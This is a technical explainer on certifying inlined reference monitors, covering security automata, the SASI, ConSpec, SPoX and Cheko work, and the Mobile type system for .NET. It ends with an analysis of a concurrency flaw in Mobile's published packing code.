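# Certifying inlined reference monitors without trusting the rewriter

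## What an inlined monitor is and why its rewriter is normally trusted

An inlined reference monitor is a set of security checks that a tool called the rewriter (or inliner, in some papers) inserts into a program before the program runs. The checks halt the program when it is about to break a security policy. This lets a user run a restricted version of an untrusted applet or advertisement without changing the operating system. The rewriter has to put the right checks in the right places, and users normally trust that it does. With certification, they don't have to trust the rewriter, because a separate program, the certifier, examines the rewritten code and rejects it unless it can prove that the code obeys the policy.

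*A Language-Based Approach to Security* (Schneider, Morrisett and Harper) defines a reference monitor as a mechanism that observes a running system and halts it whenever it is about to violate a policy. An operating system does this when a system call transfers control to the kernel, which checks the call. The transfer takes time, and the kernel can enforce only policies about operations that cross its boundary. *SASI Enforcement of Security Policies* (Erlingsson and Schneider, 1999) points out that a browser might need rules about how helper applications use the browser's resources, and those uses may involve no system call. Inlined checks run as ordinary instructions inside the program, where they can inspect method calls and their arguments directly.

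### One program, before and after

A standard example policy forbids a program to send anything over the network once it has read a file. Here is a small program that may or may not comply:

```
if wants_report:
    text = read(file)
send(status)
```

The value of `wants_report` comes from the user, so one run is harmless and another breaks the policy. A rewriter might turn the program into this:

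```
state = 0                    # inserted
if wants_report:
    state = 1                # inserted
    text = read(file)
if state != 0: halt          # inserted
send(status)
```

Erlingsson and Schneider's tool, SASI, produced essentially this from Java bytecode. It inserted two instructions before the file read to set a variable to 1, and three before the network write to load the variable, test it and call a failure routine if the test failed. To do this, SASI placed a copy of the whole policy before every instruction, deleted the parts that could not apply to that instruction, which was usually all of them, and compiled the rest.

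A *security-relevant event* is an operation that the policy covers, here `read` or `send`. A *trace* is the sequence of such events in one run. The original program has two possible traces, (send) and (read, send). The rewritten one has (send) and (read), because the second run now halts before the send. The inserted test is called a *guard*.

A *security automaton* is a state machine that accepts exactly the traces the policy allows. Schneider, in *Enforceable Security Policies*, defines it by a countable set Q of states, a subset Q₀ of initial states, a set I of input symbols and a transition function δ: Q × I → 2^Q. The automaton starts with the current set Q′ equal to Q₀. On each symbol s it replaces Q′ with the union of δ(q, s) over all q in Q′, and it rejects as soon as Q′ is empty. For the example, let state 0 mean "no file read yet" and state 1 "a file has been read", with 0 as the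 initial state:

- δ(0, send) = {0} and δ(0, read) = {1}
- δ(1, read) = {1} and δ(1, send) = ∅

The trace (read, send) takes Q′ from {0} to {1} to ∅, so the automaton rejects it. The automaton accepts (send, read), which leaves Q′ at {1}.

The *policy state* is the state this automaton is in, given the events so far. It is a property of the run and isn't stored in memory. The *monitor state* is the variable in the rewritten program, `state` above, that is meant to record the policy state. The two can differ, and they do so briefly even in the correct program, because `state` becomes 1 just before the read happens. Much of the work of certification is showing that they agree at the points where it matters.

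Automata like this express *safety properties*, policies that every forbidden run violates at some definite point, after which nothing can repair the violation. For example, a program cannot take back a message it has sent. Formally, Γ is a safety property if for every run σ outside Γ there is an i such that, for every continuation τ, the first i steps of σ followed by τ also lie outside Γ. Schneider showed that a monitor that only watches a run and stops it can enforce no policies other than safety properties. It cannot enforce "every request eventually gets an answer", since any unfinished run might still deliver the answer. It also cannot enforce information-flow policies, which depend on a comparison between runs. Some safety properties are unenforceable too. A monitor cannot enforce "no user waits more than a fixed number of seconds", because it cannot stop time from passing.

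All of this requires *complete mediation*, meaning that every security-relevant event passes through the monitor. The program must not be able to jump around the guard or overwrite `state`. For Java, SASI relied on the type safety of the bytecode to prevent both, since the program could not access the added variables and the inserted code contained no label to jump to. Policies also had to forbid dynamic class loading and reflection, which would have given programs a way around the monitor. The policy must also define its events completely. Schneider warns that a system may offer many ways to send a message, some of them "buried deep within the bowels of the target", and the policy's definition of `send` has to include them all.

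### The trouble with trusting the rewriter

The *trusted computing base* is everything that must work correctly for the security claim to hold. With an ordinary inlined monitor, it includes the rewriter, where a mistake can go unnoticed. Suppose an optimizer inside the rewriter wrongly concludes that the `wants_report` branch never runs and drops the line `state = 1`. The resulting program starts normally and passes its guard every time, even when it sends after reading.

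Erlingsson and Schneider dealt with this by keeping SASI simple. They described its components as "neither large nor complex" and left out whole-program analysis that could have removed redundant checks, because they worried it would enlarge the trusted computing base. The resulting code is slower. Schneider and colleagues describe the same tradeoff, in which optimization keeps the overhead of inlined checks low, but each optimization routine adds another place where a bug could let a violation through.

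Most later rewriters were larger. The lecture slides *Model-Checking In-lined Reference Monitors* list disassemblers, binary analysis tools, compilers, optimizers and code generators among their components. *Security Policy Enforcement by Automated Program-Rewriting* (Hamlen, 2006) explains that a production rewriter must correctly analyse a wide range of third-party code, work quickly enough not to delay loading, and produce output that runs at close to the original speed. It is also convenient to write a specialized rewriter for each new policy, so the number of trusted tools grows over time. *Aspect-Oriented Runtime Monitor Certification* (Hamlen, Jones and Sridhar, 2012) puts one Java rewriter at over 900,000 lines, including the general-purpose code-weaving system it was built on.

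In 2006 Hamlen thought that proving a realistic rewriter correct once, for all inputs, might be far off, since researchers had only just managed such proofs for realistic compilers. Sridhar and Hamlen (2011), in *Flexible In-lined Reference Monitor Certification*, add that the proof would not stay valid for long. In web advertising, for instance, new attacks force frequent changes to the monitors' details, and a proof about the old rewriter does not cover the changed one. Easier proofs would weaken both objections, but they would not help where a third party does the rewriting, a case the lecture slides raise, because the recipient would still have to believe that the third party ran the proved version.

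### Checking the output instead

The alternative is to leave the rewriter alone and check each program that comes out of it. Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider (2005), in *Certified In-lined Reference Monitoring on .NET*, lay out the path that code then takes before it runs:

1. Untrusted code arrives.
2. A rewriter, also untrusted, takes the code and the policy and produces a self-monitoring program, in their system with annotations for the next step. The producer of the code can run the rewriter, or the recipient can.
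3. The certifier, which is trusted, takes the rewritten program and the same policy. It tries to prove *policy adherence*: every trace the program can produce is one the policy allows.
4. If the proof succeeds, the program runs with its guards in place. If it fails, the program does not run, and the failure points to a fault in the rewriter.

They argue that certifying the rewriter's output gives more assurance than trusting the rewriter alone, even when the rewriter is as small as the certifier. A bad program gets through only if both the rewriter and the certifier fail.

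A certifier is *sound* if it never accepts a program that can violate the policy. If S is the set of programs that adhere to the policy and C is the set that the certifier accepts, soundness means C ⊆ S. *Conservative rejection* occurs when a program is in S but not in C, meaning that it is safe but the certifier cannot prove it. A sound certifier must reject some safe programs because C and S cannot be equal for any interesting policy. Membership in C is decidable, since the certifier must always return an answer, but membership in S is undecidable.

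Step 3 does not use the original program, so the certifier need not repeat the rewriter's work. However, a rewriter that replaced every program with the single instruction `halt` would always pass, since stopping early never violates a safety property. *Transparency*, the property that rewriting leaves policy-compliant behaviour unchanged, rules out such a rewriter. Establishing transparency requires comparing the rewritten program with the original, which a certifier for policy adherence does not do.

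### Why guarded code is easier to verify

No algorithm can correctly decide for every program whether it obeys the policy, so the certifier's task may look hopeless. Take the program `read(file); P(); send(status)`, where `P` is any computation that itself reads and sends nothing. The program breaks the policy exactly when `P` finishes, so an algorithm that judged all such programs correctly would solve the halting problem, which is impossible.

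With the monitor inlined, the program becomes `state = 1; read(file); P(); if state != 0: halt; send(status)`. Whether `P` finishes no longer matters. The certifier only has to confirm that `P` does not write to `state`, which in a type-safe language usually means checking which instructions can access the variable. If `P` does not write to it, the guard halts every run that reaches it.

The earlier program, with its branch, shows how the proof goes when a send really can happen. Write A for the policy state. The comments give what the certifier can establish after each line:

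```
state = 0                    # A = 0, state = 0
if wants_report:
    state = 1                # A = 0, state = 1
    text = read(file)        # A = 1, state = 1
                             # branches meet: A = state
if state != 0: halt          # A = state, state = 0
send(status)                 # A was 0, so this was allowed
```

Where the branches meet, the certifier cannot determine whether a file has been read, because that depends on the user. It can establish only that A and `state` are equal. The guard lets execution continue only if `state` is 0, so A is also 0, and the automaton permits a send from state 0.

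Without the guard, the proof fails at the last line because A might be 1, and the certifier rejects the program even if no user ever asks for a report in practice. The certifier also rejects the program if the faulty optimizer has deleted `state = 1`, the bug that went unnoticed when everyone trusted the rewriter. In that case, A and `state` may differ where the branches meet. The guard still establishes that `state` is 0, but nothing about A follows from that.

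Hamlen, Jones and Sridhar work through an example using Cheko, their certifier for Java bytecode, and a policy that allows at most ten emails per run. Cheko keeps lists of constraints on the policy state and the monitor variables. At the email call, two of those lists describe a violation, but both contradict the constraint contributed by the guard, so neither violation can occur. Without the guard, there is no contradiction and Cheko rejects the code. Schneider and colleagues observe that programmers have long used the same technique with arrays. Proving that an index always stays within an array's bounds can be very hard, but the proof is immediate if the compiler emits a bounds check just before the access.

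The difficulty therefore shifts to the rewriter, which can avoid a hard proof by inserting another guard, though this makes the program slightly slower. Sridhar and Hamlen base their standard for a good certifier on this. A policy is verifiable by a given certifier if some transparent rewriter turns every program that already obeys the policy into one that the certifier accepts. A certifier could thus reject most safe programs and still be adequate, since it only has to check the programs that rewriters produce.

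### Roots in certified code

The idea of checking a program instead of trusting whatever produced it came from work on certified code in the late 1990s. *Proof-Carrying Code* (Necula, 1997) proposed that a program's supplier should also provide a formal proof that the program is safe. The recipient checks the proof with a simple validator, and has to trust only that validator and the soundness of its own policy. If someone tampers with the code or the proof, validation usually fails, and if it succeeds, the altered code is still safe. Typed assembly language, from the same years, took a similar approach using types. The compiler emits machine code with type annotations, and a type-checker verifies them independently of the compiler.

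Schneider and colleagues then combined certified code with inlined monitors and saw that both approaches benefited. A rewriter could use any optimization, however aggressive, as long as it also produced a certificate for a small trusted checker. A certifying compiler, previously limited to what automatic analysis could prove, could now insert a run-time check wherever the analysis failed. The first proposal for machine-checking inlined monitors was a type system, which Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider extended and implemented in Mobile, their system for .NET.

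Proof-carrying code does not fit rewriters exactly, though. A certifying compiler can use facts from the source program, such as where control may flow, in its proof about the machine code. A rewriter that starts from a binary usually has no source code, so Sridhar and Hamlen argue that its output needs certifiers suited to a different class of programs.

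## Writing the policy and stating what must be proved

A certifier compares a program with a policy, so its verdict is only as good as the policy. The policy writer must decide which operations count as events, whether to keep one history for the whole run or one for each object, and whether the policy should contain the enforcement code or only the rules that code must satisfy.

### Choosing the events

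In the earlier example, `read` and `send` were single steps. A real method call has arguments, takes time, and ends with either a return value or an exception, and a policy may depend on any of these. *ConSpec* (Aktug and Naliuka, 2007) describes a policy language for mobile applications in which every rule has one of three labels. A `BEFORE` rule applies when the program calls a method, an `AFTER` rule when the method returns normally, and an `EXCEPTIONAL` rule when it throws an exception. The paper's example policy forbids an application to overwrite local files. It also requires the user's approval for a network connection once the application has opened an existing file. The file rule is a `BEFORE` rule because the monitor has to act before the file opens. The approval rule is an `AFTER` rule because the monitor can't inspect the user's answer until the dialog method returns.

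In ConSpec, a call event consists of the class name, the method name, the argument values and the contents of the heap, the memory that holds the program's objects. A return event adds the return value and the contents of the heap after the call. By the time a monitor detects a forbidden return value, the method has already run, so the monitor can only stop the program from going further. ConSpec's definition of obedience therefore permits the traces L ∪ L·R, where L is the set of traces that the automaton accepts and R is the set of return events. This means any accepted trace, possibly followed by one last return that the policy disallows. To prevent an action, a policy writer has to attach the rule to the call.

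Hamlen and Jones introduce SPoX (Security Policy XML) in *Aspect-Oriented In-lined Reference Monitors*. SPoX identifies events by patterns called pointcuts, which can match a method call, a field access, or any instruction of a chosen kind, and can test arguments. Some of these tests can only be done at runtime. If a policy covers only calls whose first argument exceeds 2, for example, the rewriter inserts a test such as `x > 2`, and the certifier has to determine what that test establishes. To compare an object with a text pattern, the monitor first calls the object's `toString` method, which could have any side effect. Hamlen, Jones and Sridhar (2011) report in *Cheko* that SPoX therefore treats this call as a possible event too.

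A policy can miss relevant operations even when its pattern language is expressive. Hamlen and Jones tested SPoX on RSSOwl, a news-feed reader, with a policy that forbade network output after the program had opened a file in the Windows directory. Their pattern matched the constructors of Java's file classes. They point out that malicious code could get around it by calling a library method that takes a file name in some other way. A sound certifier could accept such a program, because the program's trace would contain no event that meets the policy's definition of a file event.

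### One history per run or one per object

For Mobile, their .NET system, Hamlen and colleagues give a policy that requires a program to open a file before reading it, allows at most three reads each time it is open, and requires the program to close it before the program ends. With O for open, R for read and C for close, the permitted histories are:

(O (R ∪ R² ∪ R³) C)^ω

Here ω means any finite or infinite number of repetitions. As written, the formula also requires at least one read before each close.

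The policy applies to each file object separately. Suppose a program opens files a and b, reads each once, and closes both. The run's events, in order, are O(a), O(b), R(a), R(b), C(a), C(b). The history of each file is O R C, so the program complies. An automaton that ignored which file each event concerned would receive O O R R C C and reject the run at the second O. Giving a single finite automaton a separate component for each file would not help, because a program can create any number of files. Hamlen and colleagues make this criticism of two earlier type systems, which tracked one global history over a finite set of events.

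A limit of ten network sends needs the opposite treatment. If each network socket had its own limit, a program could open a new socket after every tenth send. With S for a send on any socket, the permitted histories of the whole run are:

ε ∪ S ∪ S² ∪ … ∪ S¹⁰

where ε is the empty history. Mobile fits this into its per-object scheme by adding a global object that exists from the start of the program to its end, and treating every send as an operation on that object. SPoX instead has two kinds of state variable. A global variable can limit a program to creating ten files, while an instance variable, which comes into existence with each file, can limit it to ten reads of that file.

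Some policies fit neither scope. Mobile cannot express the rule that every file opened for writing must have its output linked to some encryptor object, because that rule relates two objects. Other policies extend beyond a single run. A limit of five text messages a day gives the user little protection if the count resets whenever the application restarts. ConSpec therefore has four scopes: one object, one run, all runs of one application, and all runs of all applications on the device. Aktug and Naliuka list the last two as suitable for run-time monitoring but not for static analysis of the program, so a static certificate would normally concern a single run or a single object.

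### The ten-email policy in SPoX

Here is the ten-email policy from the earlier Cheko example, in the simplified notation of Hamlen and colleagues, with comments added after the semicolons:

```
(state name="s")            ; a state variable, initially 0
(forall "i" from 0 to 9     ; repeat for i = 0, 1, ..., 9
  (edge name="count"        ; a transition called "count"
    (call "Mail.send")      ; triggered by this method call
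    (nodes "s" i,i+1)))     ; takes s from i to i+1
(edge name="10emails"       ; one further transition
  (call "Mail.send")        ; triggered by the same call
  (nodes "s" 10,#))         ; if s is 10, this is a violation
```

The `forall` line generates ten transitions, from 0 to 1, 1 to 2, and so on up to 10. In the notation for security automata, δ(i, send) = {i+1} for i from 0 to 9, and δ(10, send) = ∅. The variable `s` is the policy state, and the policy does not prescribe how the program records it. The SPoX rewriter records it in two variables, and a later section shows how the certifier checks the resulting code.

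The policy also does not specify how the monitor should respond to an eleventh call. Hamlen and Jones allow a policy writer to suggest a response, such as rolling the program back to an earlier state, but they keep the suggestion separate from the policy and do not trust it. If the rollback code broke the policy, a verifier could reject the program.

Events that match no transition leave `s` unchanged, so the program can open files or draw windows freely. But if the policy's author forgot the last three lines, `s` would stay at 10 after the tenth email and every later email would be allowed. In the core language that Hamlen and Jones first described, an operation with no matching transition was a violation. Under that rule the omission would have been harmless, but the author would have had to list every operation that the program was allowed to perform.

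### Why trusted guard code weakens the certificate

Many policy languages include enforcement code. The policy specifies where a check belongs and supplies the check itself, and the rewriter inserts it. In ConSpec, the email limit might look like this:

```
SECURITY STATE int sent = 0;
BEFORE Mail.send() PERFORM
  sent < 10 -> { sent = sent + 1; }
```

The part before the arrow is a guard, and the part in braces updates the state. If no guard in the rule holds, the call is a violation. A rewriter can translate the rule almost directly into code and place it before each call.

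According to Hamlen and colleagues, the ConSpec verifier checks that the prescribed guard code appears at every security-relevant point, but trusts the code itself. The certificate therefore establishes that the monitor is the one the policy author wrote, but not that it enforces the intended limit. Suppose the prescribed code halts the program if `sent > 10` and otherwise adds 1 and sends the email. On the eleventh call `sent` is 10, so the email is sent, yet a verifier that looks only for the prescribed code would accept the program. If a rewriter inserted the same faulty check to enforce the SPoX policy, a sound certifier would have to reject the result, because SPoX marks the eleventh call, which happens in state 10, as a violation.

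Sridhar and Hamlen add that a verifier of this kind essentially repeats the rewriting and compares the results, so it must contain much of the rewriter. Someone also has to show that the prescribed code works in every program that might receive it, which brings back the original problem of proving a rewriting strategy correct in general. Hamlen and colleagues cite case studies in which such code was extremely difficult to write correctly for large classes of untrusted programs.

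The objection has less force against ConSpec than against more permissive languages. Aktug and Naliuka modelled ConSpec on PSLang, which allowed Java-like code in its updates and gave no exact method for extracting an automaton from a policy. ConSpec's guards have no side effects, its updates have no loops, and every policy translates precisely into an automaton. Hamlen and Jones themselves considered ConSpec suitable for formal certification. In *Provably Correct Runtime Monitoring*, Aktug, Dam and Gurov use the automaton to define policy adherence without referring to inserted code. They then use ghost monitors, which a later section explains, to prove a particular rewriter correct. The weakness thus lies mainly in checking only that the code is present, and less in writing a policy as guards and updates.

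Leaving enforcement code out of a declarative policy gives its author less to get wrong, but the policy can still contain mistakes, so someone has to read it. An author could write the SPoX limit as eleven by mistake, and the certifier would check for eleven. ConSpec's own example shows how easily a short policy can go wrong. In the 2007 version, the rule for the approval dialog has a guard only for the answer "Yes". An answer that satisfies no guard is a violation, so if a user clicks "No", the monitor terminates the application, even if the application never tries to connect. The version that Aktug and colleagues published in 2008 adds a guard for refusal.

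### The adherence theorem

Let A be the policy's automaton and L(A) the set of finite traces it accepts. For a run r of a program P, let tr(r, n) be the sequence of events in the first n steps. Then P adheres to the policy if:

for every run r of P and every n, tr(r, n) ∈ L(A)

A certifier's soundness theorem is that every program it accepts adheres in this sense. (For ConSpec policies, L(A) has to include the traces with one disallowed return at the end.)

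"Every run" covers every possible input. Hamlen and Jones build this into their definition by letting a program stand for all the programs that differ from it only in the input value. Aktug and colleagues also let library calls return unpredictable results, so the theorem has to hold for any result. If any input leads to an eleventh email, the program is non-adherent, however unlikely that input is.

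The words "every n" deal with programs that run forever, such as servers. For a safety property, an infinite run is allowed if all its finite beginnings are. The soundness proof for Cheko, the Java certifier, uses this fact. Hamlen and colleagues define execution so that a forbidden event has no next step, which means that a program about to break the policy gets stuck. They treat normal termination as endless repetition of the last state, so that a finished program does not count as stuck. They then prove two lemmas about the certifier's description of the program's possible states:

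- As long as the description covers the program's real state and the certifier can take a further step, the program can take one too.
- After each step the program takes, some description that the certifier has derived covers the new state.

By induction on the number of steps, an accepted program never gets stuck, and so it never violates the policy.

Runs that terminate need an extra condition if the policy requires something to happen before the program ends. In Mobile's file policy, a file may have the history O R while the program is running, but not when the program exits, because it has not closed the file. Let H be the set of complete histories that the policy allows for a file, and pre(H) the set of all prefixes of those histories. At every step of every run, the history of each file must be in pre(H). If the run terminates normally, the history of each file must be in H. Mobile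 has a separate theorem for each condition. A program that opens a file, reads it once and then loops forever satisfies the policy, even though it never closes the file. The email policy needs no extra condition, since a program may stop after any number of emails up to ten.

### Assumptions behind the theorem

These theorems are about mathematical models of programs. They carry over to real programs only under certain assumptions:

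- The certifier can recognise every event in the code. In Java, the method that a call actually runs can depend on the class of the object at run time, so Aktug and colleagues identify the event by that class and not just by the name written in the instruction.
- The program does not use reflection, which lets it choose a method by name while it is running. Aktug and colleagues exclude reflection because it would destroy their ability to recognise calls. Code generated at run time, for example with JavaScript's `eval`, poses a similar problem. Sridhar and Hamlen report that most work on inlined monitors either rejects such code or ignores it as harmless. Rejecting it preserves the theorem. Ignoring it leaves programs that use it without a guarantee, and Sridhar and Hamlen cite case studies in which security-relevant uses of `eval` were widespread.
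- Library calls behave as the model describes. Aktug and colleagues know only the signatures of library methods, not their code, and treat each call as a single step with an unpredictable result. If a library method sent an email internally by some other route, that email would not appear in the trace. Cheko reduces its dependence on this assumption by also analysing library code that the program's control flow passes through.
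- The virtual machine enforces type safety, which protects the monitor state, as it did for SASI, and also keeps a program from disguising one operation as another. Cheko leaves this check to the Java virtual machine.
- The program's threads do not interfere with the monitor. Cheko's proof and implementation do not support concurrency, and ConSpec's authors considered only sequential programs. If nine emails have gone out and two threads both test the counter before either updates it, both tests pass and the program sends eleven. Mobile does support concurrent programs, by allowing only one thread at a time to operate on a monitored object.

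## Checking by types: the Mobile system for .NET

Java and .NET, Microsoft's comparable platform, run a type-checker on bytecode before executing it, to rule out mistakes such as treating a number as a file. Ordinary types describe what kind of value a variable holds. If types also describe which security-relevant events may already have happened, a type-checker can certify an inlined monitor.

David Walker developed a system of this kind for a small functional language in *A Type System for Expressive Security Policies* (2000). Hamlen and colleagues explain that its types track an abstraction of the global histories that could have led to each point in the program. In the file-and-network example from the first section, the history at the point where the branches meet would be "nothing, or one read".

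Walker's system has a finite set of events, so it cannot have separate events for each file when a program may open any number of files. It therefore cannot enforce the rule that a program must close every file it has opened before it exits. A 2004 system by Skalka and Smith has the same limitation.

Mobile, which Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider described in a 2005 report and a 2006 workshop paper, instead keeps a separate history for each object. A Mobile program is an ordinary program in CIL, the bytecode language of .NET, with extra type annotations. The rewriter inserts the guards and writes the annotations, and a type-checker then checks whether the result obeys the policy.

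### One history for each object

Recording a state for each variable fails when two variables refer to the same object. Hamlen's example is an object that fetches web pages, but the same problem arises with files. Suppose `f` is an open file and the program runs `g = f`, closes `f`, and then reads from `g`. A checker that changed only the type of `f` to "closed" would still treat `g` as open and accept a read from a closed file.

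Mobile gives both variables, `f` and `g`, the type File⟨ℓ⟩, where ℓ is an *object identity variable*, a name that the checker assigns to one object. A separate table, the *history map* Ψ, holds one history for each ℓ. When the program closes the file through `f`, the checker updates Ψ(ℓ), and it checks the same entry when the program uses `g`.

Each entry is a regular expression that stands for a set of traces. With O for open and R for read, Ψ(ℓ) = O ∪ OR means that the program has opened the file and may have read it once. The object's real history is always somewhere in the set. Let policy(C) be the set of complete histories that the policy allows for objects of class C, and pre(policy(C)) the set of their prefixes. If Ψ(ℓ) = H and the program performs event e on the object, the checker requires

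He ⊆ pre(policy(C))

and then changes the entry to He.

This works as long as the program's variables refer directly to the objects. It fails when the program puts a thousand files in a linked list and takes one out, because the checker cannot determine which file was taken out. Mobile's solution is the *package*, a small object with two private fields, one for the security-relevant object and one for a *state value*, which is the monitor state for that object. A program can store packages anywhere and make any number of references to them, but it cannot perform events on an object while the object is inside a package. To use the object, the program has to unpack it, which empties the package so that nothing can unpack the same object again.

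Parts of this design predate Mobile. Vault, a C-like language, already let programs test a run-time state value, and its checker used the result. But Vault relied on an analysis of which variables refer to the same object, and Hamlen and colleagues point out that such analyses cannot easily follow objects that a program stores arbitrarily on the heap or shares between threads. They took the idea of packing from L3, another experimental language.

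### The type-checker on an eight-line program

Hamlen and colleagues explain the checker with a short program, given here in simpler notation. `C` is a security-relevant class, e₁ and e₂ are events, and state value 0 stands for the history e₁e₂.

```
1  r1 = new C
2  e1 on r1
3  e2 on r1
4  r2 = new package
5  pack r1 into r2 with state value 0
6  other.field = r2              # leak to the heap
7  r3, r4 = unpack r2            # object, state value
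8  if r4 == 0: e1 on r3
   else: ...
```

In both printed versions, line 8 tests register 3 and performs the event on register 4, although line 7 has put the object in register 3 and the state value in register 4. The version above swaps the registers in line 8 to match line 7.

Let the policy be (e₁e₂)^ω, meaning e₁ and e₂ in alternation, repeated any finite or infinite number of times. The checker goes through the program as follows:

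| Line | Requirement | History map afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | the empty history ε is an allowed prefix | Ψ(ℓ) = ε |
| 2 | e₁ is an allowed prefix | Ψ(ℓ) = e₁ |
| 3 | e₁e₂ is an allowed prefix | Ψ(ℓ) = e₁e₂ |
| 4 | none | Ψ(ℓ) = e₁e₂ |
| 5 | state value 0 describes the object correctly, and the object complies with the policy | no entry for ℓ |
| 6 | `r2` is a package, so it may go on the heap | no entry for ℓ |
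| 7 | `r2` is a package | Ψ(ℓ′) = θ |
| 8 | e₁e₂e₁ is an allowed prefix | Ψ(ℓ′) = e₁e₂e₁ in the first branch |

At line 5, the checker verifies that the monitor state agrees with the policy state. If the object's entry is H and the state value stands for the set H′, the typing rule requires H ⊆ H′ ⊆ policy(C). This check fails if the rewriter attached the wrong state value. The second inclusion is needed because the checker stops tracking the object once it is in a package. The program might never unpack it again, so its history must already be complete. The checker then deletes ℓ from the map and rejects any later use of `r1`.

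By line 7 the package has been on the heap, where other code could have unpacked the object, performed more events and packed it again. The checker therefore gives the object a new identity ℓ′ and an unknown history θ. It gives `r4` the type Rep⟨θ⟩, which means that the state value, though unknown, describes that same history. The checker would reject a program that performed an event here, because nothing about θ shows that the event is permissible.

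The test in line 8 supplies the missing information. In the first branch `r4` is 0, so θ must be e₁e₂. The branch then performs e₁, which makes the history e₁e₂e₁. This is a prefix of (e₁e₂)^ω, so the checker accepts it. If the branch performed e₂ instead, the history would be e₁e₂e₂ and the checker would reject the program.

Hamlen and colleagues say that if the policy is changed to the single sequence e₁e₂e₂, the checker rejects the program because e₁e₂e₁ is not a prefix of e₁e₂e₂. By their own packing rule, however, the program would fail earlier, at line 5. The history there, e₁e₂, is only a prefix of the sequence the new policy requires, so the program may not pack the object yet.

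The original policy also doesn't allow a program to end normally after line 8, because the object's history would then be e₁e₂e₁, with no e₂ after the last e₁. The checker examines the history map at the end of the main method too, so a complete program would have to perform e₂ before finishing.

### What a state value stands for

In the implementation, each state value is a 32-bit integer k, and a table maps it to a set of histories H_k. Usually H_k contains the histories that take the policy's automaton to one particular state. Hamlen gives the example of a file class with the policy (e₁e₂\*e₃)\*, which we can read as open, read any number of times, close, and repeat. The integer 0 stands for histories that end with the file closed, 1 for those that end just after it was opened, and 2 for those that end with a read.

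When a program tests whether a state value equals 1, the checker replaces θ with θ ∩ H₁ in the branch where the test succeeds. In the other branch, it replaces θ with θ ∩ (H₀ ∪ H₂), because the state value must be one of the other integers in the table.

The rewriter can supply this table without the checker having to trust it. If the rewriter swaps the meanings of 1 and 2, the checker requires the swapped meaning when the program packs an object and infers the swapped meaning when the program tests the value, so the two still match. A bad table can make the checker reject a safe program but not accept an unsafe one. However, separately rewritten programs that exchange packages must use the same table.

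### The two theorems

The formal model labels every object o with its exact trace, written tr(o). Let h be the heap, s the stack and I the code still to run, and let an arrow stand for steps of execution. Both theorems assume that the program type-checks and that memory initially matches the types the checker assumed.

**Terminating policy adherence.** If the main method runs to completion and leaves the heap h′, then tr(o) ∈ policy(C) for every object o of every class C in h′.

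**Non-terminating prefix adherence.** If tr(o) ∈ pre(policy(C)) for every object o in h, and (h, s), I →ⁿ (h′, s′), I′ for some n, then tr(o) ∈ pre(policy(C)) for every object o in h′.

The second theorem covers programs that run forever and programs that crash. The types do not prevent a program from getting stuck by unpacking an empty package. Such a program will not have performed a forbidden event, but it may leave open a file that the policy required it to close.

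To prove the theorems, Hamlen and colleagues first show that each step of execution preserves the agreement between the types and the contents of memory. They then show that a well-typed program can always take another step unless it has finished or has tried to unpack an empty package. Both theorems follow from these two results. The traces exist only in the model. Since the theorems guarantee that no trace breaks the policy, the .NET virtual machine does not need to record them, and Mobile programs run on it without modification.

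### Finishing the job with finalizers

The rule that only compliant objects can go into a package is awkward. A program might reasonably keep a list of open files and close them later, but it cannot pack an open file because the file's history is incomplete.

Mobile gets around this with finalizers, methods that .NET calls on an object when it reclaims the object's memory. If the file class has a finalizer that closes the file, the program can put an open file into a package. The checker verifies that an object's history satisfies the finalizer's precondition whenever the program packs the object, and that the history satisfies the policy after the finalizer runs. The policy can state this packing condition separately for each class.

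The argument depends on .NET running the finalizers of all remaining objects when the program ends. The formal model doesn't include finalizers, so the two theorems don't cover this part of the system.

### The checker, its annotations and its speed

Hamlen and colleagues wrote the checker in about a thousand lines of OCaml (Hamlen's thesis gives the figure as two thousand, half of which duplicate .NET's own verifier). It handles .NET's managed bytecode, including exceptions and multiple threads, but not reflection.

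The rewriter supplies annotations that the checker would otherwise have to infer, and the checker rejects the code if any of them is false. Wherever two paths through the code meet, an annotation describes the types and histories at that point, and the checker confirms that the description covers what it has derived along each path. Annotations on methods that accept or return unpacked objects describe how the methods change those objects' histories, and annotations on calls to these methods match the caller's objects to the method's.

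Most of the remaining work is deciding whether one set of histories is a subset of another. The checker builds an automaton for each set and tests whether any history belongs to the first but not the second. Hamlen calculates that the running time can grow exponentially with the size of the policy, but only quadratically with the size of the program. Untrusted code can affect only the program's side of the comparison, so a malicious supplier cannot trigger the exponential running time.

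He tested Mobile on SciMark, a set of benchmark programs, with a policy that counted calls to various library methods. He set the limit so that the guards ran but never stopped anything. Type-checking the 32-kilobyte program took half a second. These are the total running times:

| Version | Time | Overhead |
|---|---|---|
| Original | 59.13 s | |
| Automatically rewritten | 68.92 s | 16.6% |
| Rewritten, then optimized by hand, still certifiable | 60.72 s | 2.7% |
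| Checks added by hand, not certifiable | 59.97 s | 1.4% |

About four-fifths of the automatic version's overhead came from a single matrix benchmark, whose running time almost doubled because the rewriter put guards in its inner loops. Moving some of these guards out of the loops by hand reduced that benchmark's overhead to 3%. Judging by the last two rows, certifiability itself seems to have added little overhead here, although a person had to write the optimized code and its annotations.

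The other test used a small multithreaded web server and a policy that allowed each network socket to accept at most n connections. The rewriter added about 83 bytes of instructions and 117 bytes of annotations. The checker took 0.09 seconds, and the server kept 99.97% of its throughput. Hamlen and colleagues present this as preliminary evidence that automatic rewriting can produce acceptable annotations, and say that richer policies and applications still need testing.

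### A flaw in the printed package code

A trusted library of about ten lines of C# contains the packing and unpacking operations. The checker does not verify this code. It takes the operations' behaviour from declarations in the policy, so an error in the library could undermine every certificate.

The 2005 report by Hamlen and colleagues prints the library, which works like this:

```
Pack(o, s):
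    while holding the lock on o:
        obj = o
        state = s

Unpack():
    while holding the lock on obj:
        if obj is null: raise EmptyPackage
        empty the package and return its old contents
```

A lock keeps two threads from running a piece of code at the same time, but only if both threads use the same lock. `Pack` locks the object that is going into the package. If two threads pack different objects into one package, they hold different locks and can interfere with each other. Take the web server's policy, and suppose socket a has accepted no connections while socket b has accepted all n:

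```
thread 1:  obj = a
thread 2:  obj = b
thread 2:  state = n
thread 1:  state = 0
```

The package now contains socket b with a state value of 0. When the next thread unpacks it, the guard will pass and b can accept another n connections. The type-checker would not catch this, because its rules depend on the state value in a package always describing the object beside it. The typing rules also don't require a package to be empty when a program packs something into it. A rewriter that always put objects back in their own packages might never cause the problem, but a certifier has to be sound for any rewriter's output.

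The 2005 code also declares the package as a `struct`, which C# normally copies on assignment. Two copies of one package could then each release the same object, which emptying the package was supposed to prevent.

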